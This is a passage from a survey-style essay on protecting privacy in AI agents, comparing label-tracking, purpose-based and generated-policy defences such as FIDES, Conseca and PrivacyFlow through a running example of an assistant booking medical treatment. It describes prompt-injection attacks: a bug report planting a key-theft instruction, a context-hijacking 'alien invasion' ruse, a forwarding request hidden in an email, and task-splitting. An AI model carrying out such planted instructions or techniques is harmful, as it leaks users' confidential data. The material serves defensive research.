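| Basic, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic, with policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

FIDES recovered 22 of the 38 percentage points lost in office tasks, but only 15 of the 61 lost in banking. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the trusted-action policy is designed to prevent. Performance on travel tasks fell under FIDES. The policies allowed most of the tools these tasks needed even in an untrusted context, so hiding data helped little, and GPT-4o often handled the variables badly. With the reasoning model o1, FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks and averaged 16 percentage points higher than the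 basic agent with policies across all tasks.

The tests left out two parts of the design that Maya's errand relies on. FIDES hid data only because it was untrusted, not because it was confidential, and the isolated model's answers had no fixed format. So the results are weak evidence of how often FIDES would get a note like hers through.

The attack counts are also out of date. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), every model tested resisted all 105 of AgentDojo's attacks on chat tasks without any policies. The public contest with 272,000 attempts showed that other attacks still work on newer models, but AgentDojo's original attacks are now a weak test of a defence. *Language-Based Agent Control* also presents a system that tracks confidentiality and integrity labels in typed code. With policies on, it completed about twice as many of the chat tasks as CaMeL.

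### The release in Microsoft's Agent Framework

In May 2026, Microsoft added FIDES as an experimental feature to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) illustrates it with an agent that sorts bug reports in a public code repository. One report contains a planted instruction to read a file of secret keys and post it as a comment. The report enters the context labelled untrusted and public. If the model obeys and reads the file, the contents come back labelled private. The commenting tool accepts only public data, so the enforcer blocks the comment or asks the user. If the planted instruction had been to overwrite a file, the enforcer would have refused the call because the context contained untrusted data.

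The release has three levels of confidentiality: public, private and user identity. They are ranked like military classifications, so they can't properly separate Maya's clinic from her manager. If the diagnosis is at the highest level and the team calendar is one level below, a clinic form that accepts the diagnosis will also accept the calendar. Lists of readers avoid this problem, and Microsoft uses them in examples for a separate experimental gateway that adds labels to the results of other tools.

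### Counting approvals

Blocking a call doesn't have to end the task, because the agent can ask its user for approval. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that earlier tests were unfair to labels for this reason. Those tests compared a labelled agent that received no human help with an unprotected agent that, in real use, would ask before every consequential action. They ran AgentDojo again and counted how often each agent needed approval. With GPT-5, the averages were:

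| Agent | Tasks completed without approval | Tasks completed with unlimited approvals | Approvals needed in total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, asking before every consequential action | 35.1% | 72.3% | 52.0 |
| Basic with labels, asking only if a policy fails | 43.4% | 72.3% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 78.9% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 72.7% | 80.0% | 7.3 |

Prudentia extends FIDES. It tells the model about the labels and policies so that the model can plan around them, and it makes the model give a reason before opening a variable. It can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data, which means declaring it trusted. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls. But if Maya endorsed the fake newsletter by mistake, the trusted-action policy would no longer protect her from it.

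The improvement depends on the model. With GPT-4o, Prudentia completed 42.5% of tasks without approval, while FIDES completed 50.3%. Prudentia also cost about 4 to 6 cents per task, compared with about 1 cent or less for the basic agent with labels. The approval counts are calculated as if users approve every legitimate request and stop every attack, which is optimistic if they get used to clicking "yes".

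Kolluri and colleagues deliberately gave Prudentia no equivalent option for declassifying data. They argue that whether a private fact may be released depends so much on the situation that the user should approve each message. In Maya's case, a general release of her diagnosis would let the assistant send it to anyone, although only the clinic needs it.

*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) looks more closely at what an agent can do after a block. Reading more data can't help if the problem is the recipient, because each new source can only make the label stricter. The system instead offers options that someone has authorized in advance. A person or program can approve one exact call without changing any label, or a trusted tool can produce a redacted version of the data. An agent can also avoid a block by reading sensitive material in a temporary branch, so that the main context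 keeps its label. In the paper's tests, agents completed between 64.2% and 91% of tasks, and no attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs.

*APPA* also catches leaks that a check of only the label before a call would miss. One test tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it in a single step. When the agent calls this tool, the context doesn't yet contain anything that would block the email, so a check of its current label would allow the call. Kravchenko and colleagues instead check the label that the context would have after the call, which blocks the email before the tool reads anything.

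### Who writes the labels

All these guarantees depend on correct labels. Costa and colleagues treat the user's request as trusted and public unless a developer decides otherwise. Maya's request contains the word "physiotherapy", and under that default the recipient policy would let the assistant repeat the word to her manager. If the developer restricts the request to Maya and the clinic, the context starts with that restriction, and the enforcer blocks the absence note.

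A missing label can be worse than a wrong one. In Microsoft's release, data from an unlabelled tool counts as trusted and public. If a developer forgot to label the mail search tool, the agent could send Maya's diagnosis to anyone without triggering a check. Microsoft has asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted instead. *APPA* treats a missing label as unknown. The agent can work with the data, but when a policy depends on the label, the system refuses the call unless an approved program supplies one.

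Labelling everything by hand takes a lot of work. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), a survey of such systems, judges the burden lowest when software suggests labels and a person checks them. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (2026) proposes having whoever runs a tool label its results, with "unsure" as an option that makes the agent ask its user. This would work well for a company's own tools, but an agent using a stranger's tool would have to trust the stranger to label the results honestly.

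GitHub already labels some results for agents. Its software marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. The rule takes no effort from users, but a dishonest colleague could plant instructions in a private repository and have them count as trusted.

Labels can also be too coarse. The doctor's letter may contain a diagnosis, an insurance number and advice about time off, each suitable for different people. A single label for the letter has to be strict enough for all three. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) warns of a "label explosion" in which everything ends up with every label. It suggests, among other things, replacing all-or-nothing labels with estimates of how much an output reveals about each source. Other researchers try to identify which parts of the context influenced a reply, and keep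 only the labels on those parts. Both approaches would let more legitimate messages through, but a wrong estimate could also let a secret through.

Information can also reach an output by routes that are hard to follow, such as a paraphrase or a note that the agent saves and rereads in a later session. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai and Wen, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, a tool for finding such routes. On the paper's own set of 400 scenarios, NeuroTaint was substantially better than FIDES at detecting whether information from a given source had reached a given output. NeuroTaint examines records after the agent has finished, so it can't prevent the leaks it finds.

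For email, Costa and colleagues infer the permitted readers from the sender and recipients. The doctor sent the referral to Maya, so its label is {Maya, doctor}. The clinic isn't on the list, so the enforcer would block the agent from sending it the diagnosis it needs to treat her. Correcting the label requires knowing that a physiotherapist is allowed to see a patient's diagnosis, which the email's address fields don't show.

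## What norms express that permissions and labels do not

A programmer who knows that a physiotherapist may see a patient's diagnosis can correct the label on the doctor's email by adding the clinic. Perhaps, then, norms only supply the right settings for mechanisms that security engineers already have. That depends on what the mechanisms can represent. In their usual forms, they cover the five parameters of a norm like this:

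| Parameter | Least privilege | Capabilities | Labels |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sender | The account or agent that makes the call | Whoever holds the reference | Who may have influenced the data |
| Recipient | An address or service, if the permission names one | The one resource that the reference names | The list of permitted readers |
| Subject | Nothing | Nothing | At most an owner, who may be someone else |
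| Information type | The mailbox or folder that holds it | The object that holds it | Any class that somebody has defined and applied |
| Transmission principle | Time limits and approvals | Revocation and limits on delegation | An owner's decision to declassify |

All three mechanisms handle recipients fairly well but handle subjects, the people the information is about, badly. If Maya's sister writes to her about their father's illness, the sister owns the letter in Myers and Liskov's model and can release it, even though it is about their father. Barth and colleagues say their norms differ from earlier access-control and policy languages in their treatment of the subject, of how information travels, and of what people did before or do afterwards.

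Norms also specify roles, while permissions usually specify accounts. DeYoung and colleagues distinguish the roles a person holds from the one they are acting in. If Maya's manager is also an old friend, both roles use the same email address. Maya might tell the friend about her back problem but not want it mentioned in an absence notice. A list of permitted addresses treats the two emails the same way.

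A security engineer can answer most of these objections by adding another field to the policy, though how well this works varies widely by case.

### Same diagnosis, same clinic

Maya's clinic has two web forms. One registers new patients, and the other signs people up for advertisements for braces and mattresses suited to their condition. If the assistant puts her diagnosis in both forms, the sender, recipient, subject and information type are the same, and the label {Maya, clinic} allows both flows. Only the transmission principle differs, because she gave the diagnosis for treatment, not for marketing. In a more everyday example from Dong and colleagues, sharing a postal address is appropriate when arranging a delivery but not when requesting product support.

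Security researchers have had a reply to this for twenty years, which is to make purpose a label. Byun, Bertino and Li (2005), in *Purpose Based Access Control of Complex Data for Privacy Protection*, arrange purposes in a tree, with general purposes above specific ones. Each piece of data carries a set of allowed purposes and a set of prohibited ones, and each request states a purpose $p$. The system grants the request only if

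$$p \in \mathrm{Allowed}^{\downarrow} \quad\text{and}\quad p \notin \mathrm{Prohibited}^{\updownarrow}$$

The down arrow adds everything below the allowed purposes in the tree. The double arrow adds everything above and below the prohibited ones. Suppose the tree has "any purpose" at the top, "care" and "marketing" below it, and "treatment" and "billing" below "care". Care is an allowed purpose for Maya's diagnosis, and marketing is a prohibited one. A request for treatment succeeds because treatment is a form of care. Requests for marketing and for "any purpose" both fail, since "any purpose" would include marketing.

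The stated purpose is the weak point, because users declare it themselves and the system checks only that their role entitles them to declare it. Byun and colleagues' approach can make this check quite narrow, for example by accepting a purpose only from staff with a particular assignment during working hours. But a receptionist who handles both registration and mailings could still declare "treatment" and use the diagnosis for a mailing.

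Tschantz, Datta and Wing (2011), in *On the Semantics of Purpose Requirements in Privacy Policies*, object that methods of this kind assume somebody has already labelled each action with its purpose. They instead use planning to define purpose: an action is for a purpose if it belongs to a best plan for achieving that purpose and the plan would do worse without it. In their example, a doctor sends a patient's X-ray to a private practice that the doctor also owns. If the X-ray already shows the problem clearly, sending it adds nothing to the diagnosis, so the doctor did not send it for diagnosis. If a diagnosis requires one of two specialists, sending the X-ray to either counts, although neither is strictly necessary.

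An auditor who applies this definition can sometimes prove that an action was not for treatment, because no best plan for treatment includes it. The auditor can't prove that an action was for treatment, since a doctor may do the same thing for care or for profit. The test would still rule out treatment as the assistant's reason for filling in the advertising form, because Maya's booking goes through without it.

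Purpose labels therefore answer much of the objection, but they don't replace lists of readers. *A Typestate Approach to Purpose-aware Programming* (2026), which builds permitted purposes into a programming language's types, argues that a system needs both. Information-flow control can't distinguish two flows that differ only in purpose, and a purpose check alone can't stop data from going to the wrong party for a permitted purpose.

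### Two public facts and one secret total

Maya's colleagues can all see that she is away every Thursday from ten to twelve. Anyone can look up the hours of the spinal clinic near the office, which sees patients only at that time. Neither fact is private, but together they suggest that she is having treatment.

The rule for combining labels misses this. With lists of readers, the join of two public labels is everyone ∩ everyone, which is everyone. The labels in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (2012) give the same result in a different notation. They express secrecy as a logical formula about whose permission a release requires, and public data has the formula "True", meaning nobody's. Combining two sources requires both formulas to hold, and

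$$\text{True} \wedge \text{True} = \text{True}$$

so the combination is public too.

In security, a designer can give a revealing combination of facts its own class, as Denning suggested for names and salaries, but the designer has to foresee the combination. Thirty public facts about Maya form 435 pairs and more than a billion larger sets. The class also does little if the colleague already has both facts, since nothing prevents the colleague from combining them. To protect Maya, the assistant would have to withhold one of the facts or make it less precise before it went out, and the clinic's hours may never pass through her system.

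Agents make such combinations easier. *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in agents, distinguishes between inference, which needs only a single reply, and composition, where the disclosure emerges only from two or more replies. According to the survey, controls on individual steps address composition less than any other outcome. *The Sum Leaks More Than Its Parts* (2025) models the problem with several agents that each hold one harmless table. One table might link customer numbers to names, and another might link them to devices bought. If one of the devices is a glucose monitor, someone who questions both agents can learn who probably has diabetes. *Authorization Propagation in Multi-Agent AI Systems* (2026) cites an attack that split legitimate requests into subtasks that were harmless individually but together violated security policy. The attack succeeded 71% of the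 time across 14 business scenarios, and the paper describes the general problem as unsolved.

Contextual integrity doesn't solve it either. Engelmann and Nissenbaum concede in *Countering Privacy Nihilism* (2025) that appropriate flows can still lead to inappropriate inferences. But they dispute the claim that AI can infer everything from everything, which would make it pointless to protect any type of data. They argue that many impressive inferences rest on poor proxies, such as using a phone's motion sensor to measure emotion. They propose regulating who receives data and what the recipient may do with it, as well as the type of data. A norm could forbid Maya's manager from acting on a guess about her health, though it couldn't prevent the guess.

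Labels can also block information that is harmless to share. Suppose Maya's employer wants to tell staff how many sick days its 400 employees took last year. Only the employee and the personnel office may read each record. The join of all 400 labels allows only the personnel office to read the total, because it is the only reader common to every record. The employer therefore can't share the total with staff, even though it reveals almost nothing about Maya.

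*Security theory for data flow and access control* (2025) responds by treating statistics as a different type of data from the records behind them, with a separate permitted route to outsiders, while the records stay where they are. In practice, a trusted program declassifies the statistics, and somebody has to decide which totals are safe. If Maya works in a team of two, her colleague can subtract his own sick days from the team's total to get hers. The join gives both totals the same label because the label records where a number came from, not what the recipient can learn from it.

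### Simulating what a recipient could infer

PrivacyFlow, which Staab and colleagues at Google Research and ETH Zurich presented in October 2026, tries to estimate what the recipient could learn. It is a planning procedure that language models carry out before an agent acts. Applied to the absence note, it would work as follows:

1. A triage step rates the sensitivity of each item, from public facts to sensitive information about other people. It also looks for information crossing from one setting to another, such as a diagnosis moving from healthcare to work.
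2. A planner drafts the email. For each piece of data, it records the subject, the source and the original purpose. It also lists what the manager already knows.
3. An inference step combines the draft with that background knowledge and looks for anything sensitive that the manager could newly deduce. If the draft names the spinal clinic, the diagnosis joins the list of things the email would disclose.
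4. A checker compares every flow on the list, including the deduced ones, with the norms of the setting it came from.
5. A judge approves the plan, blocks it, asks Maya or sends it back for revision. A revision should try leaving the detail out, then making it less precise, then masking it, and only then asking for consent.
6. A separate model carries out the approved plan.

The revised email would give the hours without naming the clinic. The same kind of reasoning would have helped in the earlier pilot with OpenClaw, where a meeting agenda mentioned "remediation actions" and deviations from a procedure. The agenda never mentioned the confidential audit behind them, but the manager under review could infer it from those details.

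Staab and colleagues tested PrivacyFlow on PrivacyBench, a set of 986 simulated sequences containing 5,873 tasks. Emails, notes and calendar entries arrive between the tasks. Each sensitive fact has a list of people who may know it, much like a label in FIDES, but the agent never sees the list and has to infer it from the social situation. A sequence passes on privacy only if the agent leaks nothing at any step. A separate score from 0 to 1 measures how well the agent did the tasks.

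| Model | No leak, unprotected | No leak, PrivacyFlow | Task score, unprotected | Task score, PrivacyFlow |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 51.6% | 81.7% | 0.846 | 0.759 |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 52.9% | 75.1% | 0.970 | 0.942 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 37.8% | 68.8% | 0.964 | 0.909 |
| GPT-5.4 | 38.3% | 75.3% | 0.922 | 0.766 |
| Kimi K2 | 13.0% | 58.8% | 0.892 | 0.780 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 14.6% | 69.8% | 0.902 | 0.716 |

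PrivacyFlow removed 53% to 80% of the leaks, counted by step. An instruction to preserve privacy did far less on the three models given one. On Gemini 3.8 Flash, it even lowered the share of leak-free steps from 89.5% to 86.3%.

These figures measure the whole procedure, not the inference step alone. Of 200 remaining failures with Gemini 3.8 Flash, half came from sharing more detail than the task required, such as a full street address where a ZIP code would do. Only 11.5% involved mistakes about context or inference. In one of these, the phrase "medical hardship" went to a hospital creditor that could look up the clinical records. Most failures began in planning or triage, and the inference step can do little about a fact the planner never listed.

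With Gemini 3.8 Flash, PrivacyFlow took 3.9 times as long as the unprotected agent and used 2.9 times as many tokens. It can also depend heavily on user approval. With GPT-5.4, the agent asked for approval on 89.4% of steps. Counting approved requests as passes raises the share of GPT-5.4's sequences that passed on privacy with a task score of at least 0.5 from 69.9% to 98.2%, but the "user" was another language model that agreed to nearly everything. Gemini models also generated the test cases and judged the results, so the exact percentages deserve some caution, though the improvement is large on all six models.

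Nothing outside the models enforces the approved plan. The planner can misjudge a flow, and the model that carries out the plan can depart from it. PrivacyFlow can detect a revealing combination that nobody labelled, but it doesn't provide the kind of guarantee that FIDES or TACIT does.

### Information that someone must be told

Six months later, Maya needs an operation, and the hospital's form has a field for allergies. An old letter in her mailbox describes a severe reaction to penicillin. The assistant recognizes this as health information, sees that the field is optional, and leaves it blank. It has not used a forbidden tool or leaked anything, but it has withheld information the surgeon needed.

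Engelmann and Nissenbaum describe privacy norms as requiring some flows and forbidding others, so an assistant can break a norm by saying nothing. Much research on agents leaves out this kind of breach. Dong and colleagues count an agent as preserving contextual privacy when each disclosure is appropriate for its recipient and necessary for the task, so an agent that discloses nothing passes. PrivacyBench treats a missing detail as a loss of usefulness rather than a breach. Staab and colleagues report both privacy and usefulness scores because an agent that refused every task would have perfect privacy.

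The distinction matters because protective systems tend to withhold too much. On Gemini 3.8 Flash, PrivacyFlow introduced 201 task failures on steps where neither the protected nor the unprotected agent had leaked anything. In 178 of them, the agent acted but did the job incompletely, most often by omitting an important detail or using a wrong value. Least privilege can cause the same problem earlier, since an assistant allowed to search only for messages from Maya's current doctor won't find the old letter about penicillin.

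An enforcer that allows or denies tool calls can't help when the agent makes no call. Security's best reply is that policies can contain obligations as well as prohibitions. HIPAA, for instance, gives a provider a fixed time, typically 30 days, to answer a patient who asks to see their records. In simplified form, DeYoung and colleagues would write this as

$$\text{request at time } x \;\rightarrow\; \Diamond\,(\text{answer at time } y \;\wedge\; y \le x + 30)$$

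where $\Diamond$ means "at some time in the future". If day 30 passes without an answer, a program can detect the breach and alert somebody.

Some duties have no fixed deadline. A hospital that lists an unconscious patient in its directory must offer the patient a chance to opt out as soon as this becomes practicable. A program can't use the clock to determine when that is. Byun and colleagues left obligations to future work, and DeYoung and colleagues found that two standard policy languages, EPAL and XACML, represent obligations only by a symbol with no built-in meaning.

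Sometimes a designer can turn a duty into a prohibition. If the policy forbids the assistant to submit a surgical form with an empty allergy field, the assistant has to look for an answer or ask Maya. This is a good fix for one form, but it doesn't stop the assistant from writing "none" after a careless search. It also requires the designer to know that surgeons need to hear about allergies, and it does nothing if the assistant never opens the form.

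### "Do not pass this on"

Maya eventually emails her manager about her back and asks him to keep it to himself. Confidentiality is one of the most common transmission principles, but her assistant can't enforce it, because once the email arrives, the manager can forward it or tell others about her back.

Even the written law is vague about how recipients may later use information. HIPAA lets a provider send information to a public health authority to control disease, but DeYoung and colleagues could not tell from the law whether the authority must then use it only for that purpose. A strict reading protects patients better, but it can also harm them. If a doctor sends a blood sample to a laboratory and forgets to permit billing, the laboratory may not be able to charge for the test, and the patient may go without the result.

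DeYoung and colleagues also found a loophole in the Gramm-Leach-Bliley Act, a US law on financial privacy. A company that receives a customer's information from a bank may pass it to another outside company only if the bank could lawfully have done so itself, but this restriction covers only companies that got the information directly from the bank. If the bank tells company A and A tells company B, the restriction doesn't stop B from telling company C. They propose a rule that covers any information that originated at a bank, however many companies it has passed through.

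Labels do better than this clause because they follow data through any number of steps inside a system that tracks them. "Sticky policies" extend the idea by staying attached to data when it leaves the system. They work only if the recipient's software reads and obeys them, and no software can make a person forget what they have read.

A norm doesn't physically stop the manager either. It works through his conscience, his reputation and sometimes the law, none of which depends on Maya's computer. Engelmann and Nissenbaum note that lawyers and teachers apply the duties of their profession to whatever they learn in that role. An assistant can consider such duties when it chooses a recipient, and it can state the condition in the message. It has much more control when Maya made the promise, as with her sister's letter, because a label can make her own assistant keep it.

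### Richer policies, or judgement?

One could conclude from these cases that norms are just policies with more fields. Security researchers can represent purposes, combinations of data that are revealing together, totals that are safe to release, and deadlines. A system that tracks labels can handle even confidentiality. Barth and colleagues showed that standard procedures for temporal logic can answer many questions about whether a practice complies with norms. A machine can probably store any norm that someone has stated precisely.

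Applying it is harder. DeYoung and colleagues estimated that an organization could enforce only 17 of the 84 HIPAA clauses without checking any individual disclosures. All 84 depend on recognizing what kind of information a message contains. Some also depend on a professional's belief, such as a suspicion that a patient's death resulted from a crime. More expressive formulas don't help, because the existing ones already specify what to look for and the difficulty is in finding it.

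Norms also need a source. *Privacy Conductor* (2026) notes that the logic of Barth and colleagues takes the norm as an input. Surveys can supply norms, but *Say Something Else* (2026) cites evidence that people often disagree about what violates privacy, and concludes that fixed filtering rules alone can't handle privacy for agents. Staab and colleagues go further, saying that no predefined rule, norm or policy can cover every complicated situation. Engelmann and Nissenbaum accept that some flows have no governing norm, so it can be undetermined whether those flows are appropriate. In *Respecting Context to Protect Privacy: Why Meaning Matters*, Nissenbaum says she is less interested in laying down explicit rules than in the reasoning that justifies them.

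The claim that norms are richer policies is therefore right about how to write a norm down, but choosing a norm and recognizing when it applies take judgement. That judgement isn't always needed at the moment of sending. A legal expert can approve a standard notice once, and a bank can then send it to every customer without anyone reading each copy. The absence notice with two fixed fields works the same way.

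Leaving the judgement to a model until the last moment still allows some leaks. With PrivacyFlow, the six models leaked on 3.4% to 9.3% of steps. A rule that keeps diagnoses out of absence notices would probably leak less often on that one kind of message, but it would also block the notice if Maya decided to tell her manager the diagnosis.

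## Turning norms into enforced policies

A rule fixed in advance can't adapt when Maya changes her mind, and a model that checks each message as it goes out sometimes leaks information. Several systems try to avoid both problems by separating rule-writing from enforcement. A component that interprets the situation, usually a language model, writes rules for the task. A simple enforcer then only compares each tool call with those rules, so a persuasive message can't change its decision.

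### Asking once on a phone

Researchers tried to fit permissions to context long before AI agents existed. Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues (2015), in *Android Permissions Remystified*, modified Android phones to log every use of a protected resource, such as the phone's location or its text messages. Thirty-six people used the phones for a week, generating 27 million requests, or more than 100,000 per person per day. About three quarters came from apps that were running without any sign to the user.

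Afterwards, the participants looked at screenshots the phones had taken when an app requested something sensitive. They would have blocked 149 of the 423 requests (35%), and 30 of the 36 participants would have blocked at least one. Their most common reason was that the app didn't need the data for what it was doing.

A phone can't ask about every request, because apps requested sensitive permissions about 213 times an hour. Wijesekera and colleagues tested whether it could ask once and remember the answer, using cases where the survey had asked someone twice about the same app and permission. The two answers matched only 51.3% of the time. Agreement rose to 83.5% when the app was also visible both times or hidden both times. Asking once for each combination of app, permission and visibility would have meant about 34 prompts per person in the first week, or 29 if the phone asked only when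 sensitive data would be exposed.

A phone can easily check whether an app is visible, but checking whether an email reveals too much to a manager requires some understanding of workplaces and illness.

### A policy for Maya's errand

Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, use a language model to supply that understanding. Their system, Conseca, writes a new policy for each request:

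1. Maya makes her request. Before the assistant starts, a separate model receives the request, the descriptions of the tools, and some trusted context. This is information that the developer thinks outsiders can't tamper with, such as the date and her contacts' addresses.
2. The separate model writes the policy. For each tool, it states whether the assistant may use it, what the arguments may contain, and why.
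3. When the assistant proposes a tool call, an ordinary program checks the call against the policy.
4. If the call fits, it runs. Otherwise the assistant receives the written reason and can try something else.

The stranger's newsletter may fool the assistant, but it can't change the policy, because the model that writes the policy never reads Maya's mail. Conseca is meant to guard against mistakes and outside attacks, and assumes the agent itself is benevolent.

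For Maya's errand, the policy might look like this:

```
search_mail
  allowed: yes
  sender:  ^doctor@surgery\.example$
  reason:  The referral comes from Maya's doctor.

read_calendar
  allowed: yes
  owner:   ^maya$
  reason:  The appointment has to fit her own commitments.

submit_form
  allowed: yes
  form:    ^clinic-booking$
  reason:  The clinic needs the diagnosis to treat her and the
           insurance number to bill for it.

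send_email
  allowed: yes
  to:      ^manager@office\.example$
  subject: ^Absence$
  body:    ^I will be away on \w+day from \d+:\d\d to \d+:\d\d\.$
  reason:  The manager needs the hours to plan around the absence,
           and nothing else about the appointment.
```

The limits are regular expressions, which describe permitted text. `\w+day` matches a word ending in "day", `\d` matches a digit, and `^` and `$` mean that nothing may come before or after the matched text.

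The careless email to the manager names Maya's condition, so its body doesn't fit the pattern. The program refuses the call and returns the reason, and the assistant can then write a shorter note. The email the stranger wants, with Maya's insurance details, fails because it is addressed to the billing address instead of the manager's.

A slightly looser policy would let the careless email through. In Tsai and Bagdasarian's example, a user asks her agent to answer urgent work emails, and the policy limits the sender, recipient and subject line but not the body. With similar limits, Maya's assistant could tell her manager anything in an email with the subject "Absence".

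The example also shows that a rule may not match its reason. The reason requires the recipient to be on a list of work contacts, but the pattern accepts any address that contains "@work.com", including those of employees who aren't on the list and even an outsider's address at a domain such as "work.com.stranger.example". Conseca relies on experts to catch such mismatches. It can also ask users to approve a policy before the task starts, but Maya probably wouldn't notice that the pattern is missing a `$`.

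### Twenty tasks and one planted email

Tsai and Bagdasarian tested a prototype on 20 file and email tasks, such as removing duplicate files and emailing a report. They ran each task five times with Gemini 1.5 Pro on a computer with ten fictional users.

| Policy | Average tasks completed, of 20 | Blocked inappropriate actions |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.0 | No |
| Permissive (anything except deletion) | 12.2 | No |
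| Restrictive (no changes to files or mail) | 0.0 | Yes |
| Conseca | 12.0 | Yes |

The restrictive policy was bound to score zero because every task involved writing something. The permissive policy is the more useful comparison. It completed about as many tasks as Conseca but didn't block the attack.

The attack was a single email containing a request to forward all messages about urgent security vulnerabilities to an employee. Without a policy, the agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to sort mail. Conseca's enforcer blocked the forwarding for every user request except one, which was to perform the tasks in urgent emails.

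Taking notes for an agenda from emails and summarizing important messages usually succeeded only without a policy, partly because policies blocked steps that weren't strictly necessary, such as creating an empty file before writing to it. The trial is too small to give a reliable error rate, and Gemini 1.5 Pro is an old model, but the trial does show that a generated policy can stop an attack and still let the agent do most of its work.

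### Withholding the data instead

*AirGapAgent* (Bagdasarian, Kairouz and colleagues, 2024) limits what an agent knows, whereas Conseca limits what it does. Before the agent contacts anyone, a filter model reads the user's task and data and selects only the facts the task needs. A second model then talks to the outside party with only those facts in its context. The outside party can't influence the filter because the filtering is finished before the conversation starts.

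The design defends against context hijacking, in which an outsider invents a situation that makes disclosure seem right. In one example, a restaurant's booking system tells the agent that aliens have invaded and will attack the Earth unless it reveals the user's age. To measure the effect, Bagdasarian and colleagues made up 20 users with 26 personal facts each and gave agents eight tasks, such as booking a table or preparing for a job interview.

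On an easier subset of these cases, an ordinary agent using Gemini Ultra withheld 94% of the inappropriate facts when the outsider asked for them directly, but only 45% under attack. AirGapAgent withheld 97% in both situations, but without an attack it shared only 89% of the appropriate facts, compared with 99% for the ordinary agent. On the full set, under attack, the ordinary agent withheld 33% of the inappropriate facts and AirGapAgent withheld 93%. Gemini Ultra also produced the labels for what was appropriate, which probably helped the Gemini filter.

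The filter needs a precise task. When it received only a general area, such as "health care", it withheld 68.6% of inappropriate facts, down from 96.8%, even without an attack. Maya's errand is also too broad to treat as one task. The filter would pass on the diagnosis because the clinic needs it, and the model would then have the diagnosis when it writes to her manager. The filter would have to run separately for each recipient.

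In the form-filling assistant built by Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, a supervisor model processes each blank separately. It writes an information flow card, which states who would send what to whom and for what purpose, and then decides whether to fill the blank, leave it empty or ask the user. A second model receives only the blanks that the supervisor has approved.

With Gemini Ultra, this assistant filled in 1% of the blanks it should have left empty and correctly completed 86% of those it should have filled. For a single model told to censor itself, the figures were 21% and 79%. With a supervisor that gave a yes-or-no decision without writing a card, they were 3% and 82%, so most of the improvement came from separating the two jobs. The separation mattered even more for two small Gemma 2 models. When told to censor themselves, they filled in every blank they should have left empty, but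 with a supervisor they filled in at most 2%. However, none of the forms were designed to manipulate the supervisor.

### How well models write access rules

*Privacy Conductor* argues that a model shouldn't set these rules. It puts a program between an organization's documents and the model that retrieves them. The program releases a document only if a "Policy Authority", meaning an accountable person, group or regulation, has allowed it. Opening a patient's record requires both a permitted role and an assignment to that patient, so a nurse can open her own patients' charts but not a neighbour's. The program never reads the wording of the request, so rephrasing it doesn't change which documents are allowed.

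To test the program, the researchers created 105 documents for a fictional clinic, along with 24 people who might request them, which gave 2,520 possible decisions. With labels written by hand, the program made every decision as intended. Seven configurations of six language models then wrote the labels.

The models usually recognized how sensitive a document was, matching the handwritten label on 78% to 86% of documents. They were worse at deciding who should receive it, matching the list of permitted roles on only 23% to 80%. When the program used the models' labels, it wrongly allowed 9 to 64 requests and wrongly refused 26 to 100.

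The models' labels also varied between runs. Each configuration labelled the same documents five times from identical instructions, and between 13 and 124 access decisions changed. A majority vote of the five runs didn't reliably help. With Claude Sonnet 5, the vote led to 66 wrongful releases, more than any single run.

*Privacy Conductor* says this happens because a document's contents don't determine who should receive it. That is plausible, but the test was harder than Conseca's job in one respect. Maya's request names the people involved and the purpose, whereas these models had to guess a whole clinic's rules from one document at a time. A single person also wrote the correct answers, so some of the supposed errors may be reasonable disagreements, though that doesn't explain why the models' answers changed from run to run.

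A second test gave the models much more information. They received descriptions of 214 information flows from court cases about HIPAA and had to classify each one as legal or illegal under that law. The most accurate model matched the court-based answers 87.8% of the time, but it classified 11 of the 20 illegal flows as legal. The researchers suggest having a model draft descriptions of the documents and a responsible person approve the access lists, though they haven't tested this.

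Even with perfect labels, their program wouldn't stop the careless email. Maya is allowed to read her own mail, so her assistant is too, and the program doesn't check what the assistant writes afterwards.

### Predicting what a user would allow

Another approach is to learn the rule from the user's own choices. Wu, Yang and colleagues, in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, recruited 205 people to train an imaginary assistant. Participants saw requests for data in areas such as travel and finance and chose to always share, share once, refuse once or never share.

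The researchers then built a program to predict the answers. It gives a language model the user's earlier decisions and some background, such as age range and trust in AI. It also adds predictions based on people who made similar choices. The program predicted 85.1% of decisions correctly, and 94.4% on the quarter of requests where it was most confident.

These figures cover only answers of "always" and "never" and exclude cases where people wanted the assistant to ask again. Of the 7,563 decisions, 5,244 were to share, so a program that always shared would have been right 69% of the time. With no history for a user, the prediction program did slightly worse, at 66.9%, but it refused about 70% of the requests that the user refused. One to four earlier queries raised its accuracy to 77.7%. Even with the full history, it would have shared data in 15.2% of the cases where the user said never.

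People's choices are also an unreliable guide to what they should share. Some requests included data that the task didn't need. When participants mistakenly thought this data was necessary, they shared it about 78% of the time. A program trained on their answers also picks up these mistakes.

### When the plan depends on a stranger's message

Suppose the clinic replies that new patients must also send a recent scan. Conseca generated its policy before the reply arrived, so the policy may not allow the assistant to send one. A broader policy that let the assistant send whatever the clinic asked for would also let anyone posing as the clinic obtain her files. Tsai and Bagdasarian treat this as a fundamental limit, with the example of a user who asks an agent to carry out the tasks in a manager's email. The model that writes the policy has no access to the email, so it can't tailor the policy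 to those tasks.

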